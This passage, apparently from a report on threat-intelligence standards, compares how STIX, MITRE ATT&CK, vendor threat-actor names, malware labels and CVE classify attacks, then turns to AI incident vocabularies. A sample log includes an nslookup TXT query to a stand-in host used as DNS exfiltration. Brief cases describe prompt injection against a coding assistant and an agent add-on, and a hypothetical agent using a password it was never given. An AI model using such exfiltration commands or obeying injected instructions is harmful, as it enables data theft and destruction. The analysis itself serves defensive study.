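Jin and colleagues call STIX the de facto standard for structured threat data. Its flexibility probably helped it spread. A company could adopt STIX and keep its analysts' own terms, add fields for its own products, and leave out whatever it did not know or did not want to share. But this freedom also means that two companies can both follow the standard and still describe the same attack so differently that software cannot match their accounts. A similar format would give AI developers the same freedom, and they would have a stronger reason to use that freedom because they would be describing their own failures.

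Defenders of the flexible design can reply that companies would have used a strict format less, and the list of industries supports them. It had no term for the legal sector until OASIS added one in April 2025, nearly four years after version 2.1 came out. Because the list is open, senders could write "legal" in the meantime. With a closed list, they would have had to choose a wrong industry, leave the field empty or wait. Similarly, users who needed the missing incident object made their own long before the committee agreed on anything.

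But a strict format need not be complicated. Jin and colleagues suggest that senders use so little of STIX because it is complex, and a field with five permitted terms is simpler to fill in than one with an open list and a space for notes. Still, closed lists would not have prevented many of the errors in their data. No committee could keep a complete list of hacking groups, and a sender who types a malware name into the threat actor field has misunderstood the field, whatever terms it allows.

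The draft incident suite uses both closed and open vocabularies. A sender must choose an incident's status from a closed list, which includes suspected and confirmed. If the sender reports how recoverable the damage is, it must use fixed categories. The type of incident has an open vocabulary. If Alder and Birch used the suite, readers could compare how many of their incidents were confirmed, but the two companies could still file the same database test under different types.

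## MITRE ATT&CK, a list of attack techniques

STIX has an object for an attacker's method, but senders can call the method whatever they like. Cedar wrote "Phishing link", and another firm might write "fake login email". With MITRE ATT&CK, a numbered list of methods, both firms can write T1566, which always means phishing. MITRE introduced the list in 2015, and threat reports, government warnings and competing security products now use its numbers.

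### How MITRE builds and revises the list

ATT&CK describes an attacker's behaviour at four levels:

| Level | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Tactic | The attacker's goal | Credential Access: getting account names and passwords |
| Technique | A method of reaching the goal | T1552, Unsecured Credentials |
| Sub-technique | A narrower version of the method | T1552.001, Credentials In Files |
| Procedure | What a particular attacker did | A thief opens `deploy.env` and copies a password |

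The levels do not form a strict hierarchy, because one technique can serve several tactics. An attacker might use a stolen account (T1078, Valid Accounts) to get into a network or to keep access to it later.

MITRE's analysts read accounts of real attacks and group similar procedures under one technique. The technique's entry cites those accounts as examples and gives advice on detection. Virkud, Inam and colleagues explain in *How does Endpoint Detection use the MITRE ATT&CK Framework?* (2024) that MITRE admits only verified behaviour, so the newest methods may be missing. Outsiders can propose changes, and the latest release credits twelve people, some from companies such as NEC.

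That release, version 20, came out on 13 October 2026. The release notes, MITRE's *Updates* (2026), list 15 tactics, 227 techniques and 479 sub-techniques for Enterprise, the part that covers organisations' computers and cloud services. Mobile phones and industrial control systems have their own lists. Six years earlier, according to MITRE's *Updates* (2020), Enterprise had 14 tactics, 177 techniques and 348 sub-techniques.

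MITRE usually publishes a new version of ATT&CK every April and October. It marks replaced entries as revoked and entries dropped without a replacement as deprecated. It also publishes the changes in a form that software can read, so a company can update revoked labels automatically.

Splitting a category causes more trouble. In April 2026, MITRE split the tactic Defense Evasion into Stealth and Defense Impairment, according to its release notes for version 19. The security company SCYTHE describes Stealth as attackers staying out of sight and Defense Impairment as attackers breaking the defences. If a company's 2025 report counted 30 cases of Defense Evasion, nobody can divide them between the new tactics unless the report also named the techniques.

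MITRE, which does much of its work for the US government, decides what goes in the list. No security vendor owns it. In February 2026, MITRE announced what it describes as an independent advisory council to support ATT&CK in the long term (MITRE, 2026).

### Labelling an attack

Suppose that someone now uses the password that Cedar's employee typed into the fake login page. Cedar's logs record four steps:

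```
14:20:11  logged in       payroll-3, from an unknown address
14:22:40  downloaded      helper.exe
14:31:05  ran command     nslookup -querytype=TXT 7f3a91c2.stats.example
15:10:52  encrypted       4,112 files
```

An analyst could label them like this:

| Step | Technique | Tactic |
|---|---|---|
| Log in with the stolen password | T1078, Valid Accounts | Initial Access |
| Download a program | T1105, Ingress Tool Transfer | Command and Control |
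| Run `nslookup` | T1048, Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol, *or* T1071, Application Layer Protocol | Exfiltration *or* Command and Control |
| Encrypt the files for ransom | T1486, Data Encrypted for Impact | Impact |

The `nslookup` command normally looks up information about an internet domain. Firewalls tend to let such requests through, so attackers hide messages in them. Here, the log line would be the same whether the attacker's purpose was exfiltration, the theft of data, or control of Cedar's computer. If `7f3a91c2` is a fragment of a stolen file, T1048 is the right label. But the string might instead identify the computer to the attacker's server, which replies with the next instruction, and then T1071 fits better.

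To choose between the labels, the analyst needs to see the server's reply or find out whether `helper.exe` had just read a confidential file. *A Graph-Based Approach for Mapping Kernel-Level Telemetry to MITRE ATT&CK* (2026) reports that work by MITRE's own Center for Threat-Informed Defense shows that many techniques are ambiguous in isolation and that analysts need context to infer intent. Without that context, an analyst can apply both labels, but anyone who counts labels will then count one command twice.

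Alder's agent-17 raises a different question about purpose. T1552.001 describes how it got the database password, but the tactic above that technique, Credential Access, covers adversaries who are trying to steal passwords. Alder could give the technique and leave out the tactic. (MITRE's separate list for attacks on AI systems, ATLAS, has its own categories.)

### How rival products label the same attacks

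Vendors attach ATT&CK numbers to their detection rules, which are searches that raise an alert when a matching action appears in a computer's logs. Virkud and colleagues compared the rules of three commercial products, Carbon Black, Splunk and Elastic, as of October 2022. ATT&CK then had 191 Enterprise techniques. A product "covers" a technique if at least one of its rules has that technique's number.

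| Product | Labelled rules | Techniques covered | Coverage | Coverage by high-risk rules only |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Carbon Black | 867 | 105 | 55% | No risk scores |
| Splunk | 911 | 100 | 52% | 25% |
| Elastic | 473 | 92 | 48% | 26% |

The last column counts only rules the vendor rated as high risk or above. About half of Splunk's and Elastic's coverage therefore came from rules that analysts are less likely to act on. Sigma, a public collection of rules from many contributors, covered 79% of techniques, but it also lost coverage when the researchers removed its less critical rules.

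Fifty-three of the techniques had no coverage in any of the commercial products. The researchers could explain most of these gaps. For 21 techniques, known detection methods work badly, often because they would raise too many false alarms. Others happen outside the systems the products monitor, such as when an attacker studies a company's social media pages. A vendor that tried to reach 100% coverage would probably make its product worse.

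Virkud and colleagues then looked for rules aimed at the same threat, meaning the same malware, hacking group or software flaw. They found 37 threats that appeared in the rules of at least two products. For 19 of them, no two products shared a label, and the labels matched completely for only one threat. Across all 37 threats, the products agreed on 37 of 296 labels, or 12.5%.

That figure probably makes the disagreement look worse than it is. The hacking group FIN7, for example, uses many methods. Splunk's rules for it had nine techniques, Elastic's had three and Carbon Black's had two, with no overlap. The vendors may have written rules for different parts of FIN7's attacks. Virkud and colleagues recognise this problem but did not calculate how often vendors agree when their rules detect the same action.

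They did find cases where the rules overlap and the labels differ. Elastic and Splunk each have a rule that would catch the `nslookup` command on Cedar's computer. The rules are nearly identical, but Elastic labels its rule T1071 and Splunk labels its own T1048. An analyst using Elastic would suspect that the attacker was controlling the computer, while one using Splunk would suspect data theft. In another case, a single Windows command would set off rules in all three products. Carbon Black and Elastic label it as a misuse of access tokens, which Windows uses to track a user's permissions. Splunk gives it two other labels, one of which refers to using the command line.

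Carbon Black also labelled its own rules inconsistently. It had two rules for the NotPetya malware, and any event that triggered the narrower rule would also trigger the broader one. But only the broader rule had the label for stealing passwords from a computer's memory. A company has nothing to gain from contradicting itself, so much of the inconsistency probably has honest causes, including overlapping definitions and the judgement of whichever analyst wrote the rule.

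A MITRE employee told the researchers that varied labels might even be a good thing. That is reasonable when labels are meant to help an experienced analyst understand an alert, since both readings of the `nslookup` command are worth investigating, but much less so when a regulator or customer wants to count incidents by technique. Regulators and customers also couldn't judge how serious an incident was from its technique number, because rules with the same number had widely varying risk scores even within one product.

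Still, competing security companies all use ATT&CK, a common reference that none of them owns, and they tie its terms to behaviour that can be observed on a computer. Virkud and colleagues could therefore compare two rules, check that both would catch the same command, and show that the labels differed. If each vendor had used private names, nobody could have measured the disagreement. AI developers do not yet have an equivalent reference, and a term like "misalignment" is harder to check because it does not refer to any particular action in a log.

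### How well people and AI models agree

Researchers have also tested labellers who have no product to sell. In *A Structured Cyber Threat Intelligence Dataset Using STIX 2.1 Entities* (July 2026), two cybersecurity researchers independently judged 147 technique labels from 25 threat reports. Their agreement was 0.67 on a weighted form of Cohen's kappa, which penalizes near misses less than complete disagreements. That is well above chance, but they only judged whether existing labels were correct, which is easier than choosing labels from the whole list.

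Agreement also varies a lot between techniques. In *Evaluating Open-Source LLMs for Multi-Label ATT&CK Technique Classification on CTI Reports* (2026), annotators labeled summaries of 83 real incidents, choosing from 211 techniques. Mean kappa was 0.68 across the 114 techniques measured, but 49 fell short of the study's quality threshold of 0.7. Clear guidelines may help. *CTI2TTP* (2026) gave annotators explicit instructions for common sources of disagreement, and their kappa was 0.76 before they resolved their disagreements. However, the two studies used different texts, so the higher kappa may not come from the instructions alone.

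The most recent test of automated labellers is less encouraging. *A SoK for SoCs* (September 2026) gave three AI models 45 reports from sandboxes, isolated computers that run suspicious files and record what they do. Masquerading (T1036), in which attackers disguise something malicious as legitimate, was a correct label for 21 reports, and all three models missed it. For ten techniques, every model missed real cases and reported false ones. Agreement between models is therefore weak evidence that their labels are right.

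Comparing reports at the level of tactics would remove some errors. *Beyond Single Reports* (2026) found that a third of automated misclassifications were between techniques with similar meanings, and 79% of those pairs shared a tactic, so at least a quarter of the misclassifications would not change a count of tactics. But Elastic and Splunk would still disagree about `nslookup`, because their labels belong to different tactics.

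### Coverage as a selling point

Vendors can easily advertise the percentage of ATT&CK techniques that their products cover. Virkud and colleagues found 19 security vendors that used ATT&CK in their marketing. A company that assesses cyber risk told them that its customers often chose products by their advertised coverage, and took 90% coverage to mean "90% secure".

A company can count a technique as covered when it has a single detection rule for it, even if that rule catches only one of the many ways attackers can carry it out. MITRE warns against using the list this way and tells companies not to treat it as a bingo card.

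Vendors have a reason to inflate their coverage, and they could do it by adding labels to existing rules or writing weak rules for techniques that are hard to detect. But the three products in the study left about half of the list uncovered. This suggests that the incentive has distorted the advertising more than the labels, though the study did not test vendors' motives.

### MITRE's product evaluations

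MITRE has also tested products itself since 2019, with vendors volunteering to take part. *MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations*, an account by Trifiletti published by MITRE, describes how MITRE staff choose real attackers, study their methods and imitate them in a simulated company network. For each step of the attack, they record how the product responded. According to Sophos, one of the vendors, MITRE graded each alert a product raised in the 2025 round as "general", "tactic" or "technique", depending on how much the alert explained. Together these grades make up the product's "analytic coverage".

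The evaluations avoid much of the trouble with `nslookup`. MITRE's staff play the attacker, so they know why they ran each command, and every product faces the same attack. Vendors cannot improve their results by choosing a more convenient label.

Vendors can, however, choose which results to advertise. According to Techzine's *Why did so many security vendors abandon MITRE's stresstest?* (2025), Palo Alto Networks claimed the only perfect score in 2023, but CrowdStrike and Microsoft also advertised 100%. Those two companies counted some steps as detected that their products had recorded without raising an alert.

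In the next round, MITRE added harmless activity to test whether products would raise false alarms. According to Techzine, some vendors responded with settings that triggered alerts for all kinds of harmless activity. A customer's security team could not have worked with those settings.

The 2025 round produced more perfect scores. CrowdStrike (2025) announced "flawless" results, with 100% detection, 100% protection and no false positives. According to a footnote on CrowdStrike's results page, the detection figures come from the "configuration change run", a run with changed product settings. Allie Mellen of Forrester, a research company that advises buyers, had already warned about such claims after the 2024 round. In SecurityWeek's *MITRE Posts Results of 2025 ATT&CK Enterprise Evaluations* (2025), Mellen says that a vendor claiming 100% has probably shown only favourable results, used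 unrealistic settings or treated the test as a competition.

Even the full results are hard to compare. Forrester's *MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations Return* points out that vendors entered different combinations of products in 2025, some including network or cloud security tools. CrowdStrike, Cybereason and ESET produced a handful of alerts for each attack, while Sophos and Trend Micro produced hundreds. MITRE does not rank vendors or state which outcomes are better, which keeps it out of commercial disputes but leaves interpretation largely to the vendors' marketing departments.

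### The withdrawals of 2025

About 30 vendors took part in 2022 and again in 2023. The number fell to 19 in 2024 and 11 in 2025. Microsoft, SentinelOne and Palo Alto Networks all announced that they would miss the 2025 round, and their reasons were much alike:

- **Microsoft** withdrew in June. Selvaraj (2025), in *Microsoft's participation in MITRE ATT&CK® Evaluations*, wrote that the company wanted to focus on its internal security programme and on new products.
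- **SentinelOne** withdrew in September. SentinelOne (2025) wanted its engineers to work on projects for customers.
- **Palo Alto Networks** withdrew on the same day as SentinelOne. Palo Alto Networks wanted to speed up product development. Its statement also repeated its 100% results from the previous two rounds, "without delays or configuration changes".

Infosecurity Magazine's *Major Cyber Threat Detection Vendors Pull Out of MITRE Evaluations Test* (2025) reports how MITRE's chief technology officer, Charles Clancy, explained the withdrawals. Clancy agreed that the tests take up a lot of vendors' time, and said that MITRE had let its annual planning forum with vendors lapse and might have made the latest test too hard. Igal Gofman, an engineering director at CrowdStrike, was harsher and called the evaluations "vendor theater" that served publicity more than security. CrowdStrike still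 took part that year and advertised the result.

A company that expects a bad result can also stay away, although there is no evidence that any of the three did. Because companies can choose not to take part, averages are misleading. Techzine reports that two-thirds of participants detected less than half of the attack steps in 2024, while the average in 2025 was close to 100%. Products may have improved, but many of the weaker participants had also left. Voluntary incident reports from AI developers could show a similar improvement if the companies with the worst records stopped publishing.

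MITRE (2026) has since promised a unified scoring framework and "no vendor-controlled results" for the 2026 round. It also has competition from PIVOT, a test run by the British company SE Labs. Poireault (2026), in *Major Cyber Threat Detection Vendors Turn to New UK Testing Program*, reports that CrowdStrike, Palo Alto Networks, Sophos and others have joined PIVOT. Analysts from the research companies Forrester and Gartner will examine the underlying evidence and add their own interpretation before SE Labs publishes the results, expected in January 2027.

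## Security companies' rival names for hacking groups and malware

Rival security companies share MITRE's numbers for attackers' methods, but each has its own names for the attackers. One group of Russian military hackers, which broke into the computers of the US Democratic Party in 2016, has at least nine:

| Company | Name for the group |
|---|---|
| Mandiant | APT28 |
| CrowdStrike | Fancy Bear |
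| Microsoft | Strontium, later Forest Blizzard |
| Kaspersky | Sofacy |
| Trend Micro | Pawn Storm |
| ESET | Sednit |
| Google | Frozenlake, later Lake Relic |

Some of the names follow a system. CrowdStrike calls Russian groups bears and Chinese groups pandas, while Microsoft calls them blizzards and typhoons. Listing all nine names as synonyms mostly works for a group this well studied, but each name stands for a company's conclusion about which attacks belong together, and companies often reach different conclusions.

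### Where one group ends and another begins

Analysts almost never observe a hacking group directly. *Hesperus is Phosphorus* (Roa, Suarez-Roman and Tapiador, 2025) describes how analysts collect the traces of break-ins, such as malware and server addresses, and link attacks that have traces in common. When a security company has linked enough attacks, it gives the cluster a name. Mandiant starts with a provisional number, such as UNC2452, and may later decide that the cluster belongs to a group it already knows.

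Suppose two security companies, Dogwood and Elm, each investigate attacks on their own customers. Dogwood's product runs on customers' computers, so its analysts group attacks by the malware used. Elm monitors network traffic and groups attacks by the server behind them.

| Attack | Victim | Traces | Dogwood's name | Elm's name |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Bank | Malware K | Tin Otter | Not seen |
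| 2 | Hospital | Malware K | Tin Otter | Not seen |
| 3 | Shipping company | Malware K, server S | Tin Otter | Group 61 |
| 4 | Ministry | Malware K, server S | Tin Otter | Group 61 |
| 5 | University | Server S | Not seen | Group 61 |
| 6 | Airline | Server S | Not seen | Group 61 |

One group may have carried out all six attacks, or server S may belong to a criminal who rents it to anyone, in which case Elm has mixed at least two groups together. Neither company can settle the question alone, because Dogwood has no records from the university or the airline, and Elm has none from the bank or the hospital.

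If a crosswalk lists Tin Otter and Group 61 as equivalent, readers will blame the same people for the attacks on the bank and the airline, though no evidence connects the two attacks. Anyone who adds Dogwood's four attacks to Elm's four will also count eight attacks instead of six, because two of them appear in both sets.

Security researchers made a similar mistake with Winnti, a program for controlling computers remotely. They attributed attacks that used it to a single "Winnti Group", but later found that several groups had used the program. MITRE, which gives hacking groups its own ID numbers, warns that security companies' definitions of a group may overlap only partly. It tries to match the companies' names using public reports, but it cannot see their private evidence.

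That private evidence differs a great deal between companies. *A different cup of TI?* (Bouwman, Griffioen and colleagues, 2020) compared the indicators, such as malicious addresses, that two leading companies sold to their customers. Both companies claimed to track the same 22 groups, but their indicators for each group overlapped by only 2.5% to 4.0% on average. The companies may still have been tracking the same groups, since a large group uses many servers and each company may have found different ones. But a customer who bought both services could hardly have confirmed this from the indicators.

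### What happens when software merges the names

Roa and colleagues collected 3,287 group names from public sources, along with eight lists of aliases. Their software joined any two names that a list treated as the same, which produced 977 clusters. Of these, 62% contained a single name, and only 2% had 15 or more. The confusion is therefore concentrated in a few groups, mostly ones that many companies have written about.

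The software also wrongly merged two Russian groups, APT28 and APT29, which Mandiant, the company that named them, considers separate. The US government used the name "Grizzly Steppe" for an operation in which the two groups separately broke into the Democratic Party's computers. One list gave Grizzly Steppe as another name for APT29, and because the name was also linked to APT28, the software treated them as one group.

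In the largest cluster, which had more than 500 names, a single doubtful link between "Dark Seoul" and "Bronze Edison" accounted for about 35% of all supposed alias pairs. One bad entry can thus make a crosswalk wrong about thousands of pairs.

### Names as advertising

When a newspaper writes "Fancy Bear", it also publicises CrowdStrike's research. Axios' *Cyber firms explain their ongoing hacker group name game* (2022) reports that a company gains reputation when its name for a group catches on. Juan Andrés Guerrero-Saade, a security researcher, told SecurityWeek that any company that denied marketing played a role was "being disingenuous".

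Five major companies told Axios that they would still have different names if their marketing departments were not involved. They have an interest in saying so, but there is some evidence that publicity does not always decide the name. In 2021 CrowdStrike's chief executive testified to the US Senate about the SolarWinds breach, in which hackers got into government networks through a software update. CrowdStrike's *Naming Names* explains that he called the attackers "StellarParticle", rather than one of the company's more famous "Bear" names for Russian groups, because CrowdStrike had not independently verified who they were.

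Google is an even better test, because after it bought Mandiant in 2022 it had two teams naming groups. Infosecurity Magazine's *Threat Intelligence* reports that Google's older team used the name Frozenvista for a cluster that Mandiant already called UNC2589. Google kept using two sets of names until 2026, probably because of separate records and habit. Rivalry cannot explain it, since the teams no longer competed for customers.

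The best evidence against the companies comes from Joe Slowik of the data company Dataminr. He told CyberScoop, in *CrowdStrike, Microsoft aim to eliminate confusion in threat group attribution*, that analysts at different companies agree fairly well in private, but that published reports often leave out the overlaps. Marketing or promises of confidentiality to customers could explain the omission, but differences in the companies' evidence could not. An outsider who has only the published reports cannot tell whether the reason was marketing or confidentiality.

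### Two attempts at common malware names

Malware should be easier to name than hacking groups, since two companies can examine exactly the same file. Antivirus products nevertheless label files very differently. *MalDICT* (2023) gives an example of labels for a single file:

| Label | What it tells the reader |
|---|---|
| `Backdoor.Androm.99` | Andromeda family |
| `Win32/Gamarue.1234` | The same family under another name |
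| `W32.TrojanDownloader.Wauchos.A` | The same family under a third name |
| `Malware (ai Score=99)` | Probably harmful, family unknown |

Another product in the example wrongly assigns the file to Zeus, a different family.

In 1991 the Computer Antivirus Research Organization (CARO), an informal group of researchers, agreed on a scheme for naming viruses by family and variant. Later versions added the type of malware and the system it runs on. Microsoft still follows the scheme, so its label `Worm:Win32/Gamarue` gives the malware's type, system and family.

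CARO had more success getting companies to agree on a format for names than on the family names themselves. A company that found a new virus had to send its customers an update at once, often before it knew what its rivals had called the virus. Once the name had appeared in products and news reports, changing it would also have caused confusion. CARO could not make companies change names, and there were soon far too many new viruses for a few researchers to compare.

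MITRE tried a different approach in 2005 with the Common Malware Enumeration (CME), which the US government funded. Companies could keep their own names, and MITRE would add a neutral number. For example, an email worm that spread in early 2006 was known as Blackworm, Nyxem, MyWife and Kama Sutra, and MITRE numbered it CME-24.

This suited large outbreaks, when millions of people were reading about one worm under several names. But attackers were already moving to smaller, targeted attacks with many variants of each program. To number them all, MITRE would have had to decide thousands of times whether two files were versions of the same program. The public also had less need for the numbers as famous worms became rarer, and the project petered out.

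Researchers now use software such as *AVClass2* (2020) and *ClarAVy* (2025) to reconcile the labels afterwards. *MOTIF* (2021) measured how well this can work, using 3,095 malware files whose families analysts had already identified in published reports. The researchers treated known aliases as one name and then took a vote among the antivirus products:

| Result of the vote | Files |
|---|---|
| Correct family | 1,178 |
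| Wrong family | 719 |
| No clear majority | 1,198 |

The vote was right for 62% of the files that had a clear majority, but for only 38% of all files. For 577 files, no product gave the correct family. A crosswalk could not have fixed these errors, because the researchers had already applied one. Many products had named a related family, or one with similar abilities, instead of the correct one.

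Malware that analysts write reports about may be harder to label than other malware, so the general error rate could be lower. But earlier studies may have been too optimistic, since *AVClass2* notes that some included only files on which the products largely agreed. Security companies also have little reason to improve their labels, because a product can block a file without identifying its family, and customers pay mainly for the blocking.

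### The Microsoft and CrowdStrike crosswalk

On 2 June 2025, Microsoft and CrowdStrike announced that they had matched their names for more than 80 hacking groups. Microsoft's *Announcing a new strategic collaboration to bring clarity to threat actor naming* said that Google's Mandiant and Palo Alto Networks would also contribute. Outsiders had matched companies' names before, but they had to infer from public reports whether two companies meant the same group. Microsoft and CrowdStrike analysts compared their findings directly.

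Roa and colleagues found 241 CrowdStrike names and 200 current Microsoft names in public sources. The first crosswalk therefore covered roughly a third of CrowdStrike's names and two-fifths of Microsoft's. It may have been more complete than those fractions suggest, because some groups are probably known to only one of the companies.

CrowdStrike wrote that a single naming standard "is not practical and may not be possible". Its head of adversary research, Adam Meyers, told CyberScoop that with a crosswalk, no company has to adopt another's judgement. If Dogwood later learns that someone else carried out attack 4, it can change which attacks it attributes to Tin Otter without asking Elm. A Microsoft spokesperson told Lyons of The Register that imposing one standard could also affect the intelligence itself.

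Just Security's *Call Them What They Are* rejects this argument. It says the industry could agree on common names but lacks the will, since NATO has common names for foreign aircraft and doctors have common codes for diseases. The comparison with aircraft is weak because several countries can photograph the same plane and see that it is the same one. But the article has a point about the 80 groups in the crosswalk, because the companies kept both names even after agreeing that they were tracking the same groups. Having different evidence is no longer much of a reason to use separate names for those groups.

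The published lists were awkward to use. heise online's *APT and cybercrime gangs* found that CrowdStrike's version was a spreadsheet inside a zip file. Microsoft's version also included other companies' names but didn't make clear who had coined them or whether those companies agreed with the match. Slowik said the effort was "not useless, but it's not revolutionary either".

Progress since then has been modest. Microsoft (2026) has kept its list up to date, but the working group that the two companies planned does not appear to have produced the independent, industry-wide reference that Meyers hoped for. In July 2026 Google replaced its two sets of names with a third. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *Updated Cyber Threat Actor Naming System* (2026) explains that numbered names such as APT28 are hard to remember and tell defenders too little. Google keeps other companies' names searchable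 in its product and reused some familiar ones. For example, the group widely known as Sandworm became Sandworm Relic. But Google warned that exact comparisons between companies' groups "are rarely possible". According to the headline of Baba Aissa's article *Google change le nom des hackers les plus traqués au monde* (2026), the change leaves the main problem unsolved.

### Why software flaws were easier to number

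Software flaws have had neutral identifiers since 1999, when MITRE started Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE). In 2014, researchers at Google and at the Finnish company Codenomicon independently found the same flaw in OpenSSL, software that encrypts web traffic. Codenomicon called it Heartbleed and gave it a logo. Each discovery had its own CVE number, so the programme kept CVE-2014-0160 and rejected the other as a duplicate. Codenomicon still got publicity, and others could refer to the flaw by its CVE number.

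The duplicate was easy to recognise because anyone could examine OpenSSL's code and see that both teams were describing the same mistake. Dogwood and Elm cannot examine a hacking group in this way. Companies also have a practical reason to use the number, because they need to tell customers which flaw an update repairs. They can use it without agreeing on who exploited the flaw or how serious it is.

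Under CVE's counting rule, two flaws generally get separate numbers if developers can fix them separately. A similar rule would count Alder's twelve test runs, which shared one cause, as one incident.

The CVE programme is only partly independent of companies. Hundreds of organisations, including Microsoft and Google, assign the numbers for flaws in their own products. A company might prefer not to acknowledge a flaw, but outside researchers who found it can dispute a refusal. The programme also depends on US government money, which came within a day of running out in April 2025.

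Some AI incidents would suit this kind of numbering. If Alder's agent broke into the computers of Cedar, the accountancy firm, both companies would have records of the same logins. A neutral body could give the break-in one number for both reports, even if Alder described a failed test and Cedar described an attack, so readers would know not to count it twice. But if the agent never left Alder's own systems, nobody outside the company would know about the incident.

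## Existing vocabularies for AI incidents

Several organisations already classify AI incidents. MITRE's ATLAS lists attacks on AI systems, the AI Incident Database (AIID) records harms described in public reports, and the OECD has a reporting form that it hopes governments will adopt. ATLAS is modelled on ATT&CK, the AIID's founders used CVE numbers as one of their models, and the OECD drew partly on its records of product recalls. The three therefore treat a case like Alder's database test differently. In that test, an agent used a password that nobody had told it to use, and there was no attacker.

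### ATLAS and attacks on AI systems

MITRE's *ATLAS* (2020) has the same structure as ATT&CK, and its case studies show the techniques in use. Many of the techniques are specific to AI. In data poisoning, for example, an attacker plants misleading examples in a model's training data.

The July 2026 release of ATLAS has 16 tactics, each an adversary's goal, so ATLAS suits Alder no better than ATT&CK does. One case study describes criminals who found unprotected credentials on their victims' systems and used them to run AI models at the victims' expense. The same technique numbers would fit agent-17, but MITRE also assigns a tactic to each step of a case study, so a case study of Alder's test would have to list an adversary's goal for every step.

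The 68 case studies have the same limit. None covers a model that acted wrongly without an attacker or a researcher playing that role. MITRE marks 18 as incidents and the rest as exercises, in which researchers tried out or demonstrated an attack. "ChatGPT Package Hallucination" comes closest to an exception, because chatbots sometimes recommend nonexistent software packages without being attacked. MITRE included the case because an attacker could publish malware under one of the invented names, and it lists the security companies that studied the problem as the "actor".

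ATLAS takes the same approach to agents. In February 2026 MITRE investigated OpenClaw, an open-source assistant that people run on their own computers. MITRE (2026) noted that OpenClaw can act "without continuous human oversight", but its investigation focused on the techniques attackers would use. In one case study, a researcher published an add-on with hidden instructions, and 16 users ran it within eight hours. ATLAS treats an agent's independence as something for an attacker to exploit, which makes sense in a list for security teams, who need to know what attackers do.

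An AI developer can use ATLAS to report what rivals do to its model, but ATLAS has no category for what the model does on its own. One of the 18 incidents is a developer's accusation against its competitors. Anthropic reported that DeepSeek, Moonshot AI and MiniMax had used about 24,000 accounts to train their models on the answers of its model, Claude. MITRE names the three companies as the actors, and the only reference in the record is Anthropic's report.

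ATLAS also has a low threshold for calling an attack an incident. In July 2025 someone slipped a prompt into Amazon's coding assistant that told it to delete users' files and cloud resources. Amazon released the software with the prompt inside, but said a syntax error had stopped the prompt from running. MITRE marks this as an incident, though it looks more like a near miss.

MITRE's own labels are not fully consistent. Researchers got malware past Cylance's antivirus product, and others got malicious emails past Proofpoint's filter. MITRE labels both attacks with the same technique, evading an AI model, but puts the first under the tactic Defense Evasion and the second under Impact. A count of incidents by tactic would therefore separate two very similar attacks.

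ATLAS has grown quickly. It had 22 case studies in June 2024, according to *Position* (Bieringer, Paeth and colleagues, 2024). *MITRE ATLAS Grows through Collaboration with CTID and Industry* (Cunningham and Dotter, 2026) credits a joint project with companies such as CrowdStrike, Microsoft and JPMorganChase for more than 45 new techniques and sub-techniques and more than 20 new case studies. MITRE now publishes a release every month. Most of the case studies are exercises, so their number reflects how active security researchers are and is a poor guide to how often AI systems are attacked.

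ATLAS is updated often but is still not fully in line with ATT&CK. Colter, Bendelac and colleagues (2024) promised in *Threat Informed Defense to Secure AI* that ATLAS would follow each new version of ATT&CK. But in July 2026, three months after ATT&CK split its Defense Evasion tactic in two, ATLAS still had a single Defense Evasion tactic.

### MITRE's AI Incident Sharing initiative

Besides its public case studies, MITRE collects reports through AI Incident Sharing, a private exchange it launched on 2 October 2024 that covers "attacks or accidents" (MITRE, 2024). Alder could report its database test there as an accident, even though ATLAS has no place for it.

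Anyone can submit an incident through a public website. MITRE then considers the submitter's organisation for membership of a "trusted community", whose members receive anonymised reports from the others. Colter and colleagues used STIX as the basis for the submissions. They wanted to collect information about:

- the AI components affected, such as a model or a dataset
- the wider system and its users
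- the attacker
- how someone detected the incident

For an accident, the third item would be blank. The list has no item for what the operator asked the agent to do or which systems it was allowed to use, so a member who read Alder's report might not learn whether the agent had gone beyond its instructions.

Anonymity probably makes companies more willing to submit reports. MITRE runs a similar exchange for aviation, where airlines also compete but safety matters to everyone. But even a well-completed report cannot help a customer choose between Alder and Birch if it leaves out the developer's name. People outside the trusted community also cannot see the reports.

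It is also unclear how much the leading AI developers take part. MITRE's partner lists from 2024 and 2026 include Microsoft but not OpenAI, Anthropic, Google or Meta. The four absent companies may still submit incidents, since the website is open to all.

### The AI Incident Database

According to *Lessons for Editors of AI Incidents from the AI Incident Database*, the AIID counts an event as an incident if someone alleges that an AI system was involved in harming, or nearly harming, people, property or the environment. This definition does not require an attacker. The editors work from news stories, lawsuits and other public documents, and often cannot establish whether the AI system caused the harm, but they can still record the incident because the definition includes alleged harm.

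One example of near harm in the AIID is Uber's self-driving cars running red lights. A separate category, "issues", covers harms that have not happened yet or that nobody has detected. The editors plan to align this category with the OECD's term "hazard".

Deciding where one incident ends has proved harder than defining "incident". Dutch authorities wrongly accused families of childcare benefits fraud, partly because of a discriminatory algorithm. It is unclear when the algorithm became part of the decisions, and when the harm ended, or whether it has, because many of the children went into foster care. The AI Incident Database (AIID) has one entry for the whole scandal, though its editors could have treated each family as a separate incident.

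Repeated failures of one product cause a similar problem. Some crashes involving Tesla's driver-assistance software have their own entries, while another entry covers a US government investigation that followed more than a dozen fatal accidents. News reports often lack the technical details editors need to tell such crashes apart, so an entry can represent one crash or many.

The editors face the same choice with disinformation. A fake video of Olena Zelenska, the wife of Ukraine's president, has its own entry, while other entries cover entire Russian campaigns. The editors' choice depends partly on how journalists told the story. AI developers could influence it in the same way when they publish their own reports. If Alder describes twelve break-ins in one blog post and Birch describes twelve in separate posts, the database may well have one entry for Alder and twelve for Birch.

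Some harms have no identifiable victim. YouTube allegedly recommended more videos about election fraud to users who already doubted the result. The AIID includes the case as a harm to society, but its editors consider such incidents perhaps the hardest to compare with others.

#### The taxonomies in the database

The AIID's basic record is short, with a title, a description, a date, and the alleged developer, deployer and harmed parties. The database also hosts several more detailed taxonomies that researchers have applied to its incidents.

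The Center for Security and Emerging Technology (CSET), a research centre at Georgetown University, built a vocabulary to classify harms in AI incidents. It separates tangible harm, such as an injury or a financial loss, from intangible harm, which people usually cannot observe directly. CSET repeatedly revised its definitions and instructions so that different annotators would give the same answers. This reduced disagreements but did not end them, partly because annotators' own backgrounds affected what they saw as harmful.

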